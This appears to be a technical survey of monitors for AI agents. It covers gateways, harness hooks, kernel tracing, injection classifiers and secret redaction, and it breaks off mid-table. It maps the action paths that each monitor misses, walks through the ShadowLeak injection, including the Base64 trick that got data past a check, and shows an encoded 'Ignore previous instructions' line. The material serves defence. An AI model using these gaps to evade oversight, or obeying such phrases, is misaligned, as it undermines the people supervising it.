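| Job handed to a scheduler or similar service | No | No | No | No | Depends |
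| Model output that the harness acts on without a tool call | No | Depends | Depends | No | Yes |
| MCP request other than a tool call | Depends | Depends | Depends | No | Yes |
| Request from a tool server to the harness | No | No | No | No | Yes |
| **Paths always checked** | **1** | **1** | **3** | **5** | **13** |

The basic gateway checks one path unconditionally. Five paths bypass every design except the kernel one: operations by the harness's own process, programs that keep running, connections through a local helper, scheduled jobs and requests from tool servers. No combination of gateways and harness checks would therefore cover these five.

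These totals count kinds of action, and agents do not use all kinds equally. An agent that only calls tools over HTTP may get nearly full coverage from the basic gateway, whereas a coding agent that mostly runs shell commands would get very little. The number 15 also depends on how finely one divides the paths. Toyoda and colleagues developed the list in discussion with two AI models and do not prove it complete.

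Some of the "no" entries are doubtful for particular harnesses. *guardscope* gives Claude Code's tools for reading and editing files as an example of operations by the harness's own process, but Anthropic documents hooks that run before those tools and can block them. Claude Code also runs hooks when a tool server requests information from the user, which *guardscope* treats as bypassing all checks in the harness. The entries for harness rules plus a gateway also seem to understate what that design can check. It gets a "no" for MCP requests other than tool calls, while the gateway alone gets "depends". Adding harness rules should not reduce what the gateway can check.

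### Checking the monitors against the kernel's records

A monitor's own log cannot show which actions it missed. Toyoda and colleagues therefore used Tracee, a separate eBPF tool, to record what happened in the kernel, and compared the monitor's log with that record.

Each design was tested with a real monitor. The test began only after the monitor had refused an action that its policy had to deny and had recorded the refusal. Without this check, a monitor that had not finished starting would seem to have missed everything. The harness then carried out 15 fixed actions with no language model involved, so that every run was the same.

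The monitor had checked any action that appeared in both the monitor's record and Tracee's, while an action that appeared only in Tracee's had bypassed it. When a monitor recorded an action as denied, the researchers confirmed that the action had left no trace in the kernel. They matched the two records partly by identifiers in the tool calls, and used a known file or address for actions that never reached the monitor.

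Seven of the 15 actions were tool calls, some over HTTP and some to local servers. The other eight wrote files, started programs, read credentials or opened direct network connections. The gateways came from Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit and, in one extra test, from agentgateway. In the runs with both harness rules and a gateway, the monitor checked all seven tool calls, but the other eight actions took effect unchecked.

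The kernel tool, ActPlane, produced almost the opposite result. It missed all seven tool calls because it had no probes at the relevant places. It checked seven of the eight other actions, allowing six and killing one program as it started, but missed a network message sent over UDP, a protocol that needs no prior connection. A monitor in the kernel could in principle cover 13 paths, but ActPlane checked only seven of the 15 actions.

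Nobody ran ActPlane together with the harness rules and gateway. Their separate results suggest that together they would have checked 14 of the 15 actions, all except the UDP message. That supports the researchers' advice to combine a monitor in the harness with one in the kernel.

The 15 actions in the runs used only four of the 15 paths in the large table: HTTP tool calls, calls over standard input and output, operations by the harness's own process, and direct connections. Everything else in the table, including every "depends", is based on analysis. All eight designs ran with one harness, Pi. A second harness, OpenClaw, ran only with the basic gateway and gave the same counts as Pi. ActPlane failed to load on two of the Linux kernel versions the researchers tried.

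A monitor can also check a tool call and judge it wrongly. If its policy allowed everything, for example, it would check every call and stop none. Toyoda and colleagues did not test whether the monitors could tell harmful actions from harmless ones.

### What the kernel adds, and what it lacks

The clearest evidence for watching below the tool call comes from ActPlane's developers, three of whom also worked on AgentSight. In *ActPlane*, Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026) took 38 rules from real software projects, such as running the tests before saving a change to the project's history. For each rule, they prepared three sequences of actions that broke it, one directly through a tool call, one through a script the agent had written earlier, and one through a file that looked harmless when the agent ran it.

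ActPlane detected 77.2% of these 114 violations. Three systems that checked only tool calls detected 34% to 40%. They did about as well as ActPlane on direct violations but caught almost none of the third kind. Many of ActPlane's misses came from the wording of the rules, which a language model had written. After the model revised the rules for the missed cases, detection rose to 94.7%, but this was measured on the same cases that had guided the revision.

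ActPlane slowed the researchers' test workloads by 1.9% to 8.4%. It can block some actions before they happen and kill the responsible program after others. In the *guardscope* test, it ran in a mode that its developers say is only for observing and killing programs.

A kernel monitor can detect that a program opened `build.env` and then connected to a particular address. It doesn't normally detect which tool call was responsible or what the message contained. A "yes" in the kernel column of the *guardscope* table therefore means less than a "yes" for a gateway, which can read the call's arguments.

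A kernel monitor cannot enforce many policies because it does not see content. Zheng and colleagues examined 1,361 policies in the instruction files that 64 popular software projects give to coding agents. A kernel monitor could enforce the 607 (45%) that concern programs, files, connections or the order of events. Another 38%, such as rules about coding style, depend on what is inside a file, and 17% concern the agent's reasoning or style of communication. Only a monitor that can read the text could enforce a rule against publishing customers' names.

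### Can a proxy on the model connection enforce anything?

Toyoda and colleagues also sorted existing products into the eight designs, relying mostly on the products' documentation. Gateways formed the largest group, and a few products, including OpenClaw PRISM, combined a gateway with checks in the harness. They put "model-only proxies", which handle only the traffic between the harness and the model, in the group with no enforcement.

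This follows from the definition of a checked path. The failing-build agent's shell command first appears in the model's response, which passes through a proxy on the model connection. The harness then sends the command to the shell without going through the proxy. If the proxy withholds the response, the harness never receives the command and cannot run it.

PIsberg's firewall is a proxy that inspects the tool definitions in each request, the tool calls in the model's responses and the results of those calls. It can also block tools by name. Akto's proxy also evaluates each response before the agent receives it.

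*guardscope* also counts permission rules in the harness as a check on programs that the harness starts. Those rules, too, apply to the proposed command and not to what the program does later. A model proxy that can refuse the same command should therefore count as a check too. It may also check something that a tool-call hook misses, since some harnesses act on the model's ordinary text without any tool call, and the proxy can inspect that text in the response.

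A hook still has advantages over a proxy. It receives the exact call that the harness is about to run, whereas the proxy has to assemble the call from a stream and interpret it the same way the harness will. The proxy must also delay the streamed response until the call is complete. If the harness acts on its own, for instance by running a start-up script, the proxy may have no model response to inspect.

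Neither proxy can follow the command after it starts. A proxy could inspect and approve `npm run build`, and a package in the build could upload the settings file. A model proxy might detect this in the next request if the package printed something suspicious to the build log, but the file would already have been uploaded. "No enforcement" is therefore a fair label for a proxy that only records traffic or filters prompts, but too harsh for one that can refuse tool calls.

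### Tools that run on the provider's servers

All 15 paths in *guardscope* start from the harness, but tools that run on the provider's own servers, such as Anthropic's web search, bypass the harness. A proxy on the model connection can read the list of tools in the request and could refuse a request that offers a server-side tool, but it cannot check each search before it runs. A kernel monitor on the laptop sees even less, because the search starts no program and opens no new connection there.

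ShadowLeak, an attack that the security company Radware reported to OpenAI in June 2025, shows how much can happen where a local monitor can't see it. It targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that spends several minutes gathering material and writing a report, and that users could connect to a Gmail account. According to Radware's *ShadowLeak*, the attacker only had to send such a user an email with hidden instructions and wait for the user to ask Deep Research to research the inbox.

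The agent then found an employee's name and address in another email, added them to a URL on the attacker's server and opened that URL with its browsing tool. The request came from OpenAI's cloud. The user's computer handled only the original question and the finished report, so no proxy, hook or kernel monitor there could have stopped the ShadowLeak theft. In EchoLeak, the data left when the user's own browser loaded an image, so a monitor on that computer had at least a chance to intercept it.

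Even inside OpenAI's systems, the position of the check mattered. The agent resisted Radware's early attempts, partly because it would not put personal details in a web address. The attack became reliable when the email told the agent to convert the details to Base64, a standard encoding that anyone can reverse, and claimed this would keep them secure. Radware explains that the model encoded the data before passing on the request, so the part of the system that opened web pages received only a harmless-looking string. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests but does not say how many it ran.

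OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August 2025 and acknowledged it on 3 September. SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Targeted in Server-Side Data Theft Attack* reported that the attack no longer worked. Radware, which sells protection for agents, recommends comparing the agent's actions with the user's goals while the agent works. For a tool like Deep Research, only the provider, or a company it gives access to, can make that comparison before the data leaves.

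Moving a whole agent to the cloud has a similar effect. Claude Code can run in sessions on remote machines, and Anthropic notes that these sessions do not read the settings file in the user's home folder. If a developer has set up a hook in that file to block dangerous commands, it won't run in a cloud session. Hooks stored with the project or set by the company can still apply, depending on how the cloud environment loads its settings.

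## Detecting secrets and hostile instructions in a message

Once a monitor can read a message, it has to decide whether to stop it. Most local monitors run a series of checks, with the cheapest first. Suppose a proxy on the model connection receives request 2 of the failing build, and the tool result now includes a few more lines:

```
DB_PASSWORD=rain-4417
DEPLOY_TOKEN=ghp_...        (36 more characters)
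... build log ...
Error: unknown option "legacyMinify"
Questions: maria.lopez@example.com
SWdub3JlIHByZXZpb3VzIGluc3RydWN0aW9ucw==
```

The message contains two secrets, a person's email address and, in the last line, a disguised instruction to the model.

### Decoding and normalising the text

The last line is Base64 for "Ignore previous instructions", but a rule that looks for those words will miss it unless the monitor decodes the line first. `llm-fw`, PIsberg's local firewall, tries to undo eleven encodings and disguises, from Base64 and hexadecimal to Morse code and pig Latin, and applies its rules to the results.

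Normalising means reducing different ways of writing the same text to one. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, has several versions of many letters, and some of its characters are invisible. A word with an invisible character in the middle looks normal to a person, but a program that compares strings treats it as a different word. In *BodhiPromptShield*, Ma, Wu and Yan (2026) tested several detectors of private data that did not normalise text. Inserting invisible characters made the simplest detector miss 99.7% of the items it had previously caught. The researchers say normalising would take the least work of the improvements their results suggest.

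### Phrase rules and similar meanings

The monitor next compares the text with phrases that are common in attacks. Each match adds points to a score, and the monitor acts if the total passes a threshold. PIsberg's rules take less than a millisecond to run. Such rules cannot easily distinguish an attack from a security manual that quotes one.

An English phrase rule also misses the same instruction in Urdu. PIsberg's second stage uses an embedding model, which turns text into a list of numbers so that texts with similar meanings get similar lists. The firewall measures how close the new text's list is to those of typical attacks. The model covers about 100 languages, so an attack in Urdu should land near its English equivalent. This stage takes under 20 milliseconds.

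### Finding secrets by format, checksum and randomness

Many services give their keys a recognisable format. GitHub's personal access tokens can begin with `ghp_`, so a simple pattern finds the deploy token. The token's last six characters are a checksum of the others, which a monitor can recompute without contacting GitHub. A random string would pass about once in 57 billion tries. The check digit on a payment card is much weaker. One random number in ten passes, so a log full of 16-digit order numbers can cause many false alarms.

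For keys without a known format, a scanner can measure how random a string looks. The usual measure is Shannon entropy, in bits per character, where *p* is the share of the string that each different character makes up:

```
H = − sum of p × log2(p)

36 random letters and digits                     about 4.65
legacyMinify    8 characters once, 2 twice       3.25
rain-4417       7 characters once, 1 twice       2.95
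```

A threshold of 4 would catch the token but miss the password, `rain-4417`. A threshold low enough to catch the password would also flag the ordinary option name `legacyMinify` and probably much of the build log. People choose passwords they can remember, and those often look less random than program code.

The best clue to the password is its label, `DB_PASSWORD=`. A later message might not include the label, for instance if the model put only the password in a search query. A monitor could store every value it finds after such a label and check later messages for exact copies.

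Exact comparison works well when the monitor already knows the secret. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine defence setups with more than 20,000 attack attempts by a language model that revised its strategy as it went. Every setup that relied on the model to protect its own secrets eventually leaked. The only setup that leaked nothing, across 15,000 attacks, used ordinary program code to check each response before delivery. Such a check cannot stop inadvertent context leakage, where an observer infers a secret from answers that never contain it.

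### Personal data has fewer fixed formats

An email address has a predictable shape, but a person's name doesn't. Detectors of personal data therefore combine patterns with named-entity recognition, in which a model labels words as people, organisations or places. Ma and colleagues compared several methods on 300 documents and on records of 493 agent tasks:

| Method | Identifiers left in documents | Identifiers left in agent records | Non-sensitive text kept (documents / records) |
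|---|---|---|---|
| Patterns only | 67.4% | 11.8% | 98% / 99% |
| Presidio, Microsoft's open-source tool | 52.2% | 8.9% | 97% / 93% |
| Patterns and name recognition, with invented substitutes | 46.7% | 1.4% | 95% / 91% |
| Rewriting by a small language model | 22.1% | 60.3% | 94% / 93% |
| The researchers' own trained detector | 7.4% | 1.8% | 80% / 75% |

The agent records were mostly regular email addresses and names, which pattern matching detects well. The documents were more varied, and only the trained detector did well on them. But it also removed a fifth to a quarter of the non-sensitive text, which could easily include an error message that a coding agent needs.

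### Replacing secrets with placeholders

A monitor that finds a secret can block the whole request, but then the developer's task stops. Redaction lets the task continue. For the database password, it works like this:

1. The monitor replaces `rain-4417` with `<SECRET_1>` and records the pair in a table on the laptop.
2. The model provider receives the request with the placeholder in it.
3. If the model writes a command containing `<SECRET_1>`, the monitor puts the password back before the harness runs the command.

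The build runs with the real settings file before the monitor edits request 2, so the redaction doesn't break the build. The harness will resend the unedited history on every later turn, so the monitor has to make the same replacement each time. If the placeholder changed, the beginning of the prompt would change too, and the provider could not reuse its cached work.

Restoring values too freely can undo the protection. Suppose a monitor replaces "Northwind Bank" with `<COMPANY_1>` in the support agent's private file. If it then restores every placeholder in the model's response, it puts the bank's name back into the public reply. The monitor therefore needs a list of the tools and recipients that may receive each real value.

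Ma and colleagues tested the timing of restoring protected values on 200 agent tasks. When restoration waited until an authorised action, 1.6% of the values were readable in the text the monitor released to the agent, compared with 51.0% when they were restored while the agent was still planning. They report that later restoration lowered helpfulness by 0.11 points on a scale from 0 to 3, but their table gives it the higher score, 2.26 against 2.15. Either way, the difference is small enough to be due to chance.

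Redaction made the agent less helpful on the same tasks. Without protection, the agent scored 2.42 for helpfulness, and 13.7% of the exact identifiers appeared in its final action. Typed placeholders such as `<PERSON_1>`, combined with the trained detector, reduced that share to 3.1% and helpfulness to 2.21. Invented names and numbers lowered helpfulness further, to 1.69, because the agent treated them as real, whereas a placeholder shows the model that something is missing.

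A reader can sometimes infer sensitive information even after names are removed. One of the researchers read 102 samples, some unredacted, without knowing which method had produced each one. The researcher could infer the sensitive fact from every unredacted sample and from 24% to 53% of the samples produced by each of four redaction methods. Each method had only 17 samples, so these percentages are rough. The table of real values is also a target, since anyone who steals it can reverse the redaction for that session.

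### When a secret arrives in two pieces

A streamed response can split a secret between two fragments, and a monitor will miss the secret unless it holds back some text until the next fragment arrives.

```
fragment 1         connect with rain-4
fragment 2         417 and retry

release at once    connect wit
hold back          h rain-4
joined             h rain-4417 and retry
```

If the longest secret has *L* characters, the monitor needs to hold back *L* − 1, because it would detect the secret once all *L* had arrived. The password has nine characters, so the monitor holds back eight. For a 40-character token it holds back 39, which delays the text by about an eighth of a second if the model writes 300 characters a second. A private key can have well over a thousand characters, but its usual text form begins with a marker line, so the monitor can wait for that line before it holds back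 more.

Placeholders such as `<SECRET_1>` can also be split on their way back, which causes the same problem. Holding back a tool call adds almost no delay, since the harness cannot run the call until it is complete.

Requests reach a proxy in pieces too. PIsberg's firewall checks a request against its fast rules while the request is still arriving and closes the connection if it finds a match. If it finds none, the request goes through the slower stages. PIsberg advertises no added delay for clean traffic, but this is hard to reconcile with the time those stages take.

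### Injection classifiers

An injection classifier is a small language model trained on examples of attacks and harmless text to estimate the probability that a text is an attack. All the injection detectors tested in *Can Open-Source Guardrails Really Protect AI Agents?*, a comparison by Mozilla.ai, were encoder-only models, which label text without generating any. The comparison suggests that developers prefer these models because attackers cannot jailbreak them, though they can still make mistakes.

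Liu (2026), in *Passing the Test You Trained On*, tested 15 classifiers on the kind of text an agent's monitor would scan. Two agent benchmarks, AgentDojo and τ-bench, include the tool calls that correctly solve each task. Liu ran those calls with no attacker and no language model, so every result was harmless. Liu then planted attacks in the same data, reran the calls and counted a result as hostile if it differed from the clean one. A third benchmark, BIPIA, consists of emails, tables and code with attacks inserted.

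The table shows false alarms at each classifier's normal setting. The last three columns show the share of attacks caught after Liu adjusted the threshold so that 1% of harmless texts caused an alarm.

| Classifier | False alarms, AgentDojo | False alarms, τ-bench | Caught, AgentDojo | Caught, τ-bench | Caught, BIPIA |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 66.9% | 0.5% | 10.1% | 0.7% |
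| PIGuard | 29.5% | 11.0% | 2.1% | 52.7% | 95.1% |
| Meta's Prompt Guard 2 (larger version) | 0.6% | 0.0% | 69.4% | 57.9% | 10.4% |
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.7% | 82.2% | 100.0% | 37.7% |

One of PIGuard's false alarms was a tool result that said only "Password updated." PIGuard gave it a score of 1.00, the maximum.

The chance of a false alarm grows with each tool result in a task. An AgentDojo task averages about 3.5 tool results. If each has a 30.1% chance of a false alarm, the chance of at least one is 1 − 0.699^3.5, or about 71%. Liu found that ProtectAI v2 would in fact have stopped 69.1% of the tasks.

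PIGuard's training data explains its odd results. Its developers trained it on 1,116 BIPIA inputs, so its high BIPIA score mostly shows that it recognises inputs similar to those. Its training data also included 53 of the 62 attack texts that Liu planted in τ-bench, but as short prompts rather than inside tool results. It caught 52.1% of the tool results containing an attack from its training data and 55.8% of those containing a new one. Liu found no exact copies of the benchmarks' attack texts in Horizon-Labs's training data, but that data did include documents and tool results with planted instructions. The form of the training text apparently matters more than the particular attacks.

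PIsberg's firewall offers ProtectAI v2 as an optional classifier. PIsberg recommends it because it roughly doubled the share of attacks that the lightweight stages catch, with almost no extra false alarms on a separate test set. Liu's figures suggest that this may not hold for tool results. However, the firewall treats the classifier's alarms more cautiously than Liu's test did, since it can send intermediate scores to a judge and reduces a block to a warning when the text only quotes or documents an attack. Only a test of the whole firewall on agent traffic would show whether the classifier's benefits hold there.

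A classifier can pass a simple demonstration and still be of little use. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) tested Prompt Guard 2 and a ProtectAI classifier on 19 bundles of agent test material, with three explicit jailbreaks as controls. Each classifier flagged all three jailbreaks but none of the bundles. How the researchers prepared and shortened the text may have affected these results.

Attackers who adapt to a detector lower its detection rate, so all of these figures are best read as upper limits.

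### A small local model as judge

A general-purpose language model can take the user's request into account, which most classifiers cannot. Given the request and a tool result, it can in principle tell whether the task calls for a particular setup script.

Liu asked two models small enough to run on many laptops, Qwen2.5-7B and Llama-3.1-8B, whether a text tried to make the assistant do something the user had not requested. At a 1% false alarm rate, Qwen caught 57.4% of the attacks in AgentDojo and 54.3% in τ-bench, while Llama caught 55.3% and 78.3%. Both did worse than Horizon-Labs, a classifier less than a twentieth of their size. On BIPIA, Qwen caught only 1% of the attacks that changed how the agent answered the user's own question. A different question to the models might have produced different results.

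A judge also has to read the hostile text, so an injection can target the judge. PIsberg leaves the local judge off by default and recommends it only for text that earlier stages found suspicious, because a small judge blocks too much harmless traffic.

### OpenClaw PRISM

Li (2026), in *OpenClaw PRISM*, describes a monitor that combines most of these checks. It protects agents that run on OpenClaw, and it works without any changes to OpenClaw's own code. Its main part is a plug-in inside the harness, with ten hooks:

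| Stage | Hooks | What PRISM can do |
|---|---|---|
| Incoming text | On receiving a message; before building the prompt | Score the text; add a warning to the prompt |
| Before a tool call | Before the call | Refuse a command, file path or network address |
| After a tool call | After the call; before saving the result | Scan the result; remove suspicious text |
| Outgoing text | Before writing a message; before sending it | Block hostile text or known types of secret |
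| Upkeep | On starting a subagent, ending a session and starting the gateway | Refuse the subagent; clear or reload saved state |

The plug-in can run alone or with up to four sidecars: a scanner, a proxy that checks permissions for tool calls, a dashboard and a file monitor. By default, the sidecars that use the network accept connections only from the same machine. PRISM also keeps a risk score that builds up over a session.

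PRISM scans tool results in two tiers. The plug-in first normalises the text and applies weighted phrase rules. If the result looks suspicious, the plug-in sends it to the scanner, which applies the rules again and may then use a local model to classify it. If the rules give a very high score, the scanner treats the result as malicious without running the model. If the model fails, the scanner uses the rules' verdict.

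Using the model only on texts that the rules give a middle score saves time. But the model then can't catch an attack that the rules score as harmless, or clear a harmless text that they score very highly.

For outgoing messages, PRISM recognises only known types of credential. It would probably catch the GitHub token in the example and let `rain-4417` through.

#### Thirty texts and a scripted judge

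Li first tested the scanner's rules alone, with no model available, on 30 texts. The rules classified 50% of the texts correctly and caught 62.5% of the attacks. Li's percentages imply 16 attacks, of which the rules caught ten, and 14 harmless texts, of which they flagged nine. Li had written some of the harmless texts specifically to provoke false alarms, so that false-alarm rate is weak evidence of how often the rules would flag ordinary traffic.

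Adding a judge raised accuracy to 86.7%, or 26 of the 30 texts. However, the judge in this run was a script, and the benchmark supplied its verdicts for 13 of the texts in place of a model's. The run shows that PRISM can use a good verdict, but not whether a real model would give one. The four remaining errors were all harmless texts that PRISM did not send to the judge because their rule scores were too high.

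#### Eighty cases with a live model

A later test used a real model, Qwen3 8B, running locally. It had 80 cases. In 47 of them, Li ran a sequence of steps through PRISM's hooks, for example fetching a page and then calling a tool. The other 33 tested permissions for tool calls, and 18 of those were attacks, such as a forbidden tool or a dangerous command. Li reports totals, which imply this breakdown:

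| Setup | Attacks through the hooks blocked (of 26) | Forbidden tool calls blocked (of 18) | Harmless cases blocked (of 36) | Time within which 95% of cases finished |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plug-in only | 20 | 0 | 7 | 0.6 milliseconds |
| Plug-in and scanner | 24 | 0 | 5 | 12.5 seconds |
| Full PRISM | 24 | 18 | 5 | 15.8 seconds |

The scanner with its live model blocked four more attacks than the plug-in alone and raised two fewer false alarms, so it got six more cases right. In a run with no model available, the scanner got four more right than the plug-in, so the live model added only two. Li highlights that full PRISM blocked 95.5% of the attacks, compared with 54.5% for the plug-in and scanner. All of that improvement came from the permission proxy, which applies fixed rules about who may call which tool and doesn't need to recognise hostile text.

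The model was also slow. With the scanner, half the cases finished in under 0.2 milliseconds because they never reached the model. The slowest took about 20 seconds, the time limit Li had set. A coding agent that made hundreds of tool calls could lose many minutes if even a tenth of the results looked suspicious. A faster computer or a smaller model would reduce the delay.

Li calls these results preliminary. The test cases were few and handwritten, and they ran in a benchmark program rather than a working OpenClaw installation.

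### How the choice of test changes the score

PIGuard did well on text that resembled its training data and badly elsewhere. Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, measured how much such resemblance can inflate a detector's score. Zavrak trained detectors to tell attacked agent sessions from normal ones. The main dataset had 605 normal and 3,797 attacked sessions across 80 tasks.

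Researchers usually divide the sessions at random into a training set and a test set. Sessions from the same task then end up in both sets, so a detector can score well by memorizing which tools go with which task. Zavrak compared this with a stricter division in which no task appeared in both sets. The scores below are AUROC, the chance that the detector rates a random attacked session as more suspicious than a random normal one; guessing gives 0.5.

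| What the detector uses | Random division | No shared tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Tool names, response lengths and a code computed from the arguments | 0.898 | 0.640 |
| The text of the arguments and responses | 0.992 | 0.891 |

Without the text, a detector that had seemed good did little better than guessing. The attacks in this dataset mostly changed what a tool received or returned rather than which tools were chosen, so equipment that reads only the headers of MCP requests would be unlikely to detect them.

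The best AUROC under the strict division was 0.975, from a standard method called XGBoost applied to text embeddings. At its normal setting, it caught 92.7% of the attacked sessions and wrongly flagged 7.1% of the normal ones. More elaborate neural networks that modelled the links between calls did worse. On a second dataset, with shorter sessions and subtler attacks, the best AUROC was only 0.784.

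Even with the strict division, the detector might partly have learned to recognise one model's style, because all the attacked sessions in the main dataset came from GLM-4-Flash, while the normal ones came from eight models. Zavrak found no sign of this in the tool names and lengths but could not rule it out for the text. The detector also needs the complete session, so it can help an investigator afterwards but cannot block a call.

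A similar doubt applies to *Machine Learning-Based Detection of MCP Attacks* (Mattsson, Nyberg and colleagues, 2026), in which several classifiers trained to recognise poisoned tool descriptions reached an F1 score of 100%. All the malicious descriptions came from one research dataset and the harmless ones came from public code repositories, so the classifiers may have learned to tell researchers' writing from software developers' writing. By contrast, a detector in the Log-To-Leak tests missed all 100 poisoned descriptions.

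Mattsson and colleagues also built a program that checks a tool's description when the model is about to call that tool, which may be too late. In the dataset they used, the poisoned tool never did the harm itself. Its description led the model to misuse other, legitimate tools, which would pass the check. A monitor would do better to check every description before the harness puts it in the prompt.

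### Tests of commercial filters

Companies also sell filters as online services, and many published comparisons come from the sellers. For example, in *A Comparative Evaluation of AI Agent Security Guardrails*, Li, Li and colleagues (2026) of Beijing Caizhi Tech compare DKnownAI Guard with three products they call competitors, from Amazon, Microsoft and Lakera.

*BELLS-O* (Waibl, Michalak and Mariaccia, 2026) independently tested 33 systems. The commercial filter Lakera Guard caught 95.6% of prompt injections but also flagged 14.4% of harmless prompts. PIGuard, which is free, caught 92.1% and flagged only 0.3% of harmless prompts. General-purpose language models caught at most 69.2%, but the researchers had asked them to look for harmful requests in general, so they might have caught more if asked specifically about injections.

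PIGuard's score here is far from the 2.1% that Liu measured on AgentDojo, but the two results are compatible because Waibl and colleagues used collections of prompts and didn't test agents, while Liu used tool results. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) cites another classifier with 98.49% accuracy on 465 examples from one of the same collections, and warns against comparing that figure with tests on unfamiliar data. Lakera Guard might also do better or worse on tool results than on these prompts, but Liu didn't test any commercial services.

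Lakera Guard caught 95.3% of the jailbreaks but also flagged 81.9% of the harmless requests. Many of the harmless requests were innocent questions phrased like jailbreaks, which Waibl and colleagues counted as harmless because they judged requests by their intent. A company that wanted to block every jailbreak attempt, whatever its purpose, would consider some of these flags correct.

Coding agents may be especially prone to false alarms. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, tested the filters built into several AI platforms and found that they often wrongly flagged code review requests as attacks.

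### Why most alerts can be false

Even an accurate detector produces mostly false alarms when attacks are rare. Suppose that 5 of every 10,000 messages are hostile, and that a monitor catches 95% of them and wrongly flags 1% of the rest:

```
hostile messages flagged     5 × 0.95        =    4.75
harmless messages flagged    9,995 × 0.01    =   99.95
real share of alerts         4.75 / 104.70   =    4.5%
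```

About 21 of every 22 alerts are false. Catching every attack would hardly help, but reducing false alarms would:

| Hostile messages caught | Harmless messages flagged | Alerts per 10,000 messages | Share of alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 95% | 1% | 105 | 4.5% |
| 100% | 1% | 105 | 4.8% |
| 95% | 0.1% | 15 | 32% |
| 95.6% | 14.4% | 1,444 | 0.3% |

The last row uses Lakera Guard's results on prompt injection. The real share of hostile messages is unknown and surely varies between agents, but 5 in 10,000 could well be too high for a developer whose agent mostly reads the company's own code. *Utility Under Attack* (2026) points out that measuring only how many attacks succeed doesn't show how a detector affects harmless traffic.

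This arithmetic supports checking in stages. If a slow judge model looked only at the 105 flagged messages, confirmed 90% of the real attacks and dismissed 90% of the false alarms, about 14 alerts would remain, and 30% of them would be real. The judge would also run about 105 times instead of 10,000. The calculation assumes that the two stages make unrelated mistakes, but a security manual full of quoted attacks might well fool both.

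A false alarm may do little damage if the monitor only replaces a harmless string with a placeholder, but it stops the task if the monitor blocks the request. A monitor can therefore reasonably redact on weak evidence and block only on stronger evidence, such as a token with a valid checksum being sent to an unfamiliar address.

Each request resends the earlier messages, so a monitor that scans every request in full repeats its alerts. If a classifier wrongly flagged the build log in request 2, it would flag the same log 99 times in a session of 100 requests. PIsberg's firewall lets the user mark a blocked prompt as harmless. It then stores a hash, a short code computed from the normalised text, and gives only a warning when an identical prompt comes through again.

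## Judging an agent's actions and where its data came from

A monitor can judge what the agent does instead of deciding whether a text is hostile. It can apply fixed rules to each tool call, add up weak warning signs over a session, or track where the data in a call came from. None of these methods helps with an action that never reaches the monitor, such as a connection that a malicious package opens during a build.

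### Fixed rules on tools and arguments

A tool policy states which calls an agent may make and with which arguments. The developer with the failing build might write this one, in which the first matching line decides:

```
shell         allow   if the command is exactly "npm run build"
shell         ask     if the command is exactly "npm install"
edit_file     allow   if the file is in the project and is not build.env
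search_docs   allow   if the query has at most 100 characters
other calls   deny
```

The monitor would refuse the agent's first command, `cat build.env; npm run build`, because it doesn't exactly match the permitted command. The agent would have to run the build command by itself, and the password would stay out of the conversation. The rule works however an attacker words an injection, because it checks only the resulting command. But if the agent had learned the password some other way, the policy would let it search for `rain-4417`. That query is well under 100 characters, and the length limit doesn't take into account where the query's contents came from.

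*AGATE* (Zhang, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes Progent, a 2025 system that enforces policies of this kind. Progent writes its policies in JSON Schema, a notation for the permitted shape of data, and can update them during a task. *Tail-risk-aware Agent Safety* (2026), which presents a rival system, tested Progent on the AgentDojo benchmark with GPT-4o. Progent wrongly flagged 37.28% of harmless cases and missed 46.51% of risky ones, only slightly better than the default setup in the same test. This result may reflect the policies used more than the mechanism that enforces them.

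Rules can also look for dangerous content in a call's arguments. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes a monitor that extracts all the text from a call, compares it with 22 patterns, and then applies the written policy. For example, a database query that ends by deleting the audit log matches a pattern. The monitor blocked all 48 attacks in a test set, but its developers assembled the set from documented techniques, so the result is weak evidence that it would block new ones. It also flagged six of 500 harmless calls, and all six were database queries with "or" in their conditions. The median delay was 8.3 milliseconds.

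### An MCP proxy that hides forbidden tools

A rule can take effect before the model chooses a tool. Uppala (2026), in *Prompts Don't Protect*, built an MCP proxy that reads each agent's role from a signed token. When the harness requests the list of tools, the proxy returns only those the role permits. It checks the role again at every call, in case the model calls a hidden tool whose name it guessed or found in an injection.

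Uppala wrote 200 tasks that tempt an agent to exceed its role. In one, a user claiming to be the chief financial officer tells an analytics agent to issue a $5,000 refund. The table shows how often each model chose a forbidden tool:

| Model | All tools visible | Permitted tools listed in the prompt, others forbidden | Proxy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |
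| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |

The zeros follow from the design, because the proxy never offered the forbidden tools. The other figures probably overstate the danger, since the test forced the model to call a tool. When Uppala let the models decline, Claude Haiku 4.5 made no call for 99% of the requests that its permitted tools could not satisfy, even when only the prompt restricted it. Qwen was much less reliable, declining 35% of these requests with the prompt alone and 86% with the proxy.

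On a single machine with no network delay, the proxy took a median of 1.5 milliseconds to prepare the filtered list, and 99% of lists took no more than 4.4 milliseconds. It did not refuse any permitted calls. Shortening the list raised Llama's success rate on 140 permitted requests from 73.6% to 82.1%, but lowered Qwen's from 59.3% to 48.6%.

The proxy doesn't protect against a permitted tool with a poisoned description, or against an agent that passes the job to another agent with wider permissions. It also allows any use of a permitted tool, even if that use is harmful.

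### A risk score that builds up and fades

When each step looks nearly harmless, a monitor can combine small signs of risk from several steps into a score. As this score rises, according to Li, OpenClaw PRISM first adds a warning to the prompt, then blocks high-risk tools, and then refuses to start subagents. Old entries expire so that one odd message doesn't restrict the agent forever.

A simple version of such a score is:

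```
new score = 0.7 × old score + signal from this step
```

*FinHarness* (2026), a monitor for financial agents, uses the same decay rate of 0.7. Its developers chose it so that an isolated weak signal of up to 0.30 drops into the lowest risk band after one quiet turn. Suppose a monitor blocks risky tools once the score passes 0.60, and an attack produces signals of 0.30:

```
step                  1      2      3      4      5      6      7
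hurried    signal    0.30   0.30   0.30
           score     0.30   0.51   0.66   (blocked)

patient    signal    0.30   0      0.30   0      0.30   0      0.30
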